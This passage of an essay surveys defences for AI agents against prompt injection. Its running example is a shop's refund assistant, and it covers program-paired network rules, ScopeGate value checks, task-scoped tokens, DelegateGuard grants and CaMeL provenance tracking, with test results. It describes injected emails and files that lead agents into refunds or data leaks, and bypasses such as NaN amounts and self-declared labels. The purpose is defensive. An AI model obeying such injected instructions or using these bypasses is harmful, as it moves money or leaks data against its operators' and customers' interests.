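OpenShell also pairs each destination with the programs that may contact it. NVIDIA's *Customize Sandbox Policies* gives an example rule that lets the package installers pip and uv reach the Python package index. Other programs in the same sandbox can't reach it unless a separate rule allows them to. The proxy identifies each program through the operating system's kernel and also checks the programs that launched it. It records a hash of each program's file on first use and blocks the program if the file changes later in the session.

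The shop could let only its refund tool contact `api.payments.example`. If instructions injected through an email then got the assistant to write and run its own script, the script couldn't call the payments service. But the instructions could get the assistant to use the refund tool instead. The proxy would allow this because the refund tool is the right program, as Tymshare's compiler was. How much pairing helps therefore depends on what the approved program can do. If that program is curl, which can send almost any request, pairing adds little.

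This control can break an agent when someone updates a program during a session or forgets to list a new one. An operator might then allow every program with a wildcard, which, as NVIDIA points out, defeats the purpose. The hash check also can't detect that a program was replaced before its first connection. OpenShell makes the main system folders read-only by default, which should prevent most of these replacements.

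### Checking the account and the amount

The operator can also restrict the values in a request. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examines whether popular agent software does this by default. In the paper, "capability gating" means a list of the tools an agent can call, not a capability in Hardy's sense. Per-call authorization determines whether the agent may make a particular call with particular values.

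He read the public source code of three products. LangChain and its companion LangGraph found the tool that the model named, usually checked the form of its inputs, and ran it. LlamaIndex checked that the tool existed and passed on whatever values the model supplied. The Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to the payments company Stripe, offered a list of permitted actions and relied on API keys with limited rights, but forwarded the model's choice of amount, customer and redirect address. All three limited which tools an agent could use, but none checked by default whether the values were authorized, so a well-formed account number would pass no matter who owned the account.

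These findings are about defaults, and a developer can add the missing check. Mellafe Zuvic doesn't claim to have found a vulnerability in any of the products, and he didn't examine the internal workings of Stripe's remote tool server. The result agrees with what Dantuluri and Sundi found in LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen.

His proposed check, ScopeGate, runs before each tool call and doesn't use a language model. It has five stages:

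1. **Scope.** Refuse any tool that isn't in the operator's policy.
2. **Authorization.** Refuse the call if a restricted field, such as the account, contains an unapproved value.
3. **Money.** Require the amount to be a finite number between zero and a ceiling.
4. **Idempotency.** Where the policy requires it, demand a trusted key that identifies repeated requests, so that nobody can run the same refund twice.
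5. **Default deny.** Refuse anything that hasn't passed every stage, including a call that causes an error.

The approved values must come from the operator, not the model. If the assistant could add accounts to the list, an attacker would first email it an instruction to add one.

In a test with LangChain's normal code, a malicious tool call changed a merchant's payout account to the attacker's. ScopeGate refused the same call because the attacker's account wasn't on the list of allowed accounts. Mellafe Zuvic wrote the call in advance instead of having a model produce it, and the payments system was a mock-up.

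ScopeGate also blocked all 48 of his prepared bypass attempts. It then refused all 29 unauthorized calls from a model acting as an attacker, even though the model learned the reason for each refusal. ScopeGate allowed all ten legitimate calls in a separate test.

An earlier prototype had accepted an amount of NaN, which means "not a number". Comparisons with NaN normally return false, so a check for amounts above the ceiling didn't reject it. Requiring the amount to be within the allowed range fixed this. Mellafe Zuvic, who works alone, wrote both the check and many of its tests, and he acknowledges that the results don't rule out other bypasses.

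A fixed list of accounts suits payouts, which always go to the shop's own bank, but it suits refunds less well because they go to many customers. The shop could instead require each refund to go to the account that made the original payment and not exceed the original amount. A custom tool could do this by accepting only a charge number and telling the payments service to refund the original card, so an attacker couldn't choose the account. An employee can handle refunds for customers who have closed the account they paid from.

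Someone who bought a $40 jacket could still inject an instruction to refund it, then keep the jacket. The charge, amount and account would all be correct. A ceiling on each refund doesn't limit how many are made, and twenty refunds of $50 come to $1,000. The shop also needs a daily limit, which it may have to raise after a product recall.

### Tokens for one task

Narrower tokens help most when they match the task. The shop could use a token that only permits reading email while the assistant summarizes the morning's complaints, and make a refund token available only when an employee starts a refund. An injected refund request would then fail during the summary, but it could still succeed during a refund task, when the proxy has the right token.

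Short-lived credentials don't help in that case because the attack happens while the assistant is working. SC Media's *After the identity fix*, a commentary by Nik Kale, describes an agent that reads a PDF with hidden instructions, changes a customer's email address and triggers a password reset. Every credential in the example is valid, narrowly scoped and short-lived.

Separate tokens also make some ordinary requests awkward. If an employee asks the assistant to read the complaints and refund everyone whose parcel never came, the assistant needs both tokens for the same task. The operator could split the task in two and have an employee check the list of customers before the refunds begin.

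### Asking whether anyone wanted it

The employee knows what they asked for. If the assistant proposes a refund while summarizing complaints, a confirmation message showing the customer, amount and account gives the employee a good chance to notice that they didn't request it. People approve most confirmation messages they see, so the shop should save them for important actions.

Tallam and Miller (2025) suggest three levels of checks in *Operationalizing CaMeL*. Reading public or openly shared data needs only a basic check, and changes within the user's own files need a simple confirmation if they involve untrusted data. Payments, outgoing emails and other actions that are hard to undo need stronger approval. Overnight refunds would therefore have to wait until someone could approve them in the morning. An employee could also approve a refund they had requested and not notice that the account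 number came from an email, so the approval message should show where the number came from.

Kale proposes checking the user's intent automatically. When an employee makes a request, software outside the model signs a record of the request and the operation it involves. Each tool then compares that operation with the one it is about to perform. A record for summarizing email wouldn't match a refund, so the refund tool wouldn't issue one.

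The hard part is deciding which operation the employee's words describe, and SC Media doesn't explain how ordinary software would do this. A model could do it, as long as it saw only the employee's words and not the emails. The record would also need to include the amount and account, because an attacker could change both if it contained only "refund".

For important actions, Kale also recommends having one tool prepare a draft and another carry it out after checking the session. Human approval is optional in this design. Without it, an injected instruction might get the assistant to use both tools in turn, and the second tool would find a recent, valid draft. For refunds, the employee should be the one who clicks to approve.

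### Capabilities issued for one purpose

Hardy's remedy was to give a program a reference that carries the right to use one particular thing. Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* (2026) proposes something similar for agents. In its example, an agent summarizing quarterly reports receives permission to read one folder for five minutes. A report contains hidden instructions to delete files, but the agent's attempt to delete them fails because its permission doesn't cover deletion.

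For a refund, the shop could issue a capability to refund charge 1042 once, up to $40, within ten minutes. In Semgrep's proposal, the agent requests the capability and the server limits what the agent receives, so an injected email could get the assistant to request a refund capability and give a plausible purpose. This wouldn't work if only an employee's click could create a capability, but then the assistant couldn't handle a second refund it discovered until the employee clicked again.

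Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues (2026), in *DelegateGuard*, tested a system of this kind for agents that pass parts of a task to other agents. A trusted program turns the user's task into a grant. Each agent can pass on some or all of its grant but can't add anything. A monitor outside the models then checks every action:

```
allow if  the actor holds the grant
     and  the purpose is within the granted purpose
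     and  the operation is in the granted operations
     and  every data label is in the granted labels
     and  the destination is in the granted destinations
     and  nobody has cancelled the grant or one it came from
```

A data label states what kind of information an action moves, such as a customer record.

The researchers compared the monitor with a static allowlist, which checks only whether the destination is on the list for that kind of work. They first ran 26 attacks, most of which stayed within the rights the agent already had. An attack counted as a leak if secret data reached a place the attacker could see. They also ran five legitimate actions to see whether each defence blocked useful work.

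Two further tests had five attacks each. In one, an agent tried to finish its work after the user had cancelled the task. In the other, it tried to send an approved destination a kind of data it was not allowed to share. The last two columns of the table below count the attacks that went ahead.

| Defence | Leaks, of 26 | Legitimate actions blocked, of 5 | Actions after cancellation, of 5 | Wrong data to an approved place, of 5 |
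|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 18 | 0 | 5 | 5 |
| Static allowlist | 3 | 0 | 5 | 5 |
| Output monitor | 0 | 4 | 0 | 0 |
| DelegateGuard | 3 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

DelegateGuard and the allowlist had the same number of leaks. DelegateGuard did better only in the last two columns, where it blocked all ten attacks. Tran-Truong and colleagues chose these tests because an allowlist can't check whether a task has been cancelled or what kind of data a request contains. The result therefore shows that DelegateGuard handles situations an allowlist can't, but not how common those situations are.

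All three leaks happened in a code-review task whose approved destination was a public comment, much like the pull request in the GitHub case. The researchers prove that no monitor of this type can prevent such leaks, because it checks the actor, purpose, operation, labels and destination but not the content. If it allows a harmless comment, it must also allow one containing a secret when those fields are the same.

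The output monitor prevented leaks by blocking any message that contained the secret. This also blocked four of the five legitimate actions, because users sometimes need their own confidential data.

DelegateGuard would stop a refund during a summary, because a grant to read complaints wouldn't include refunds. It would also stop a refund still queued after an employee cancelled the job. But once the assistant has a grant to issue refunds, the monitor doesn't check the amount, so the shop would still need limits like ScopeGate's. The labels must also be reliable. In the first set of attacks, agents declared their own labels, and an agent that declares none passes the label check. The paper recommends attaching labels in the software that fetches the data.

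### Tracking where a value came from

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, records where each value in a request came from, so a policy can distinguish two otherwise identical refunds by the source of their values. It uses two language models. The planning model receives only the user's request and writes a short program for the task. The reading model processes the emails but can't call tools, and it returns only values such as a name or number.

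*CaMeLoT* (2026) explains that the interpreter running the program tags each value with its sources and with who may read it. Before each tool call, a policy checks these tags and allows or denies the call.

If an employee asks for a summary of the complaints, the planning model writes a program without a refund step. An injected email might mislead the reading model and spoil the summary, but it can't add a refund. If the employee asks the assistant to refund a customer, the program might be:

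```
email   = read_email("parcel never came")
account = extract(email, "account number")   # source: the email
refund(charge=1042, account=account)         # policy: deny
```

Here the refund is legitimate, but the attacker supplied the account number. The shop's policy could require the number to come from the employee or the payment records. The interpreter would then refuse this refund but allow an identical one if the employee had typed the account number.

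According to Tallam and Miller, the original evaluation found that CaMeL completed 67% of tasks in AgentDojo, a test suite in which agents do everyday jobs while attackers plant instructions. Their reference list gives a different paper for CaMeL, so their account calls for some caution. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) says that CaMeL stopped nearly all the attacks and that task performance was comparable with and without it.

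*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports a lower completion rate from a later test of CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks. With its policy checks on, CaMeL blocked every attack but completed only 18 of 48 attempts (37.5%) with each of two models, about half its rate without the checks. The 67% figure covers more kinds of task and used different models, so the gap doesn't show that CaMeL got worse. On a different part of AgentDojo, a similar system called TypeGuard went from completing 15 of 21 tasks to completing 8 when its developers turned on its policies.

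In the banking tests, the separate planning step was enough on its own in 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, because the attacker needed a step that the plan for the user's task wouldn't contain. The refund injected during a summary is one of these. In the other 47, the plan could include a step that the attacker could use, so the defence depended on checking the values.

*The Devil is in the Context* (2026) tested CaMeL on newly generated attacks. The attacks succeeded 17.5% of the time without a defence and 2.5% of the time with CaMeL, but CaMeL scored only 27.5% for task completion. Another defence, PromptArmor (which shares its name with the company that reported the Cowork flaw), let 7.5% of attacks succeed and scored 90% for task completion. All these percentages would fit a set of 40 cases, in which three attacks would have succeeded against PromptArmor and one against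 CaMeL. That difference is too small to show which defence is safer, but the difference in task completion is large.

Some of the lost usefulness is avoidable. The planning model has to write code for a tool's output before anyone has seen it, so developers must describe the output's format in advance. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) calls this a modest, one-time job for each set of tools. The method also can't do tasks whose steps are in untrusted data, a harder limit described in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026). If an employee asks the assistant to follow a supplier's emailed instructions for returning goods, the planning model can't write the steps without reading the email.

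The tracking can also miss a leak. Garby and colleagues point out that CaMeL updates a variable's tag only when the program changes that variable. Suppose a program starts with a public value of "yes" and changes it to "no" if a customer's balance is low. If the balance is high, the value doesn't change and stays tagged public, so anyone who reads the "yes" learns that the balance isn't low. This leak depends on the planning model writing such a program, since the attacker doesn't write the plan.

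Garby and colleagues built a system to close such gaps, with machine-checked proofs of its guarantees. It also lets a program mark an untrusted value as trusted, which makes more tasks possible. It completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without policy checks. Only 2 of 1,296 runs under attack went wrong, both on the same task. The user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents.

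The original CaMeL evaluation also included an attack of this kind, which CaMeL's designers consider outside what the system defends against. The shop would have the same problem if an employee told the assistant to refund whatever account a customer gave. The account number is supposed to come from the email in that case, so checking where it came from wouldn't reveal a problem. An employee could phone the customer on a number from the original order to check.

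### Are detailed rules worth writing?

Rules outside the model matter most when the model is easy to fool. In a test of 27 models, Mellafe Zuvic found that 12 cheaper ones attempted the attacker's action in 60.3% of cases on average, against 18.9% for 15 leading models. One leading model, Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview, never did. A company that processes thousands of customer emails may well choose a cheap model. A $50 limit on refunds works the same way whichever model the company uses.

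But writing such rules for everything is hard. Tallam and Miller, who work for a security company, warn that a large organization with hundreds of tools can end up with duplicated and inconsistent policies. One mistake can also undo much of the protection. When Tran-Truong and colleagues added a single external destination to DelegateGuard's grants for convenience, 30 of 45 attacks succeeded, even though the monitor enforced its rules correctly.

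Even a correct rule permits some harmful uses. Tallam and Miller note that if an agent is allowed to send email, an attacker can get it to put sensitive data in a plausible message.

The first objection is a good reason to start by writing rules for a few dangerous actions. The shop's assistant can do serious harm by sending money, emailing customer data or publishing on the code host. Three rules are few enough for someone to review whenever the assistant's job changes. A company with hundreds of tools could first write rules for those that move money or send data outside, and keep the other tools away from agents that read strangers' messages.

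The second objection is weaker for money than for data. If the shop allows $200 of refunds a day and checks its accounts every three days, injected refunds can cost it at most 3 × $200 = $600 before someone has a chance to notice. A daily limit on emails doesn't protect the customer list in the same way, because one email could contain all of it. To answer a complaint, the assistant needs only the record of the customer who made it, so its lookup tool should return one record at a time and limit how many it returns in a day.
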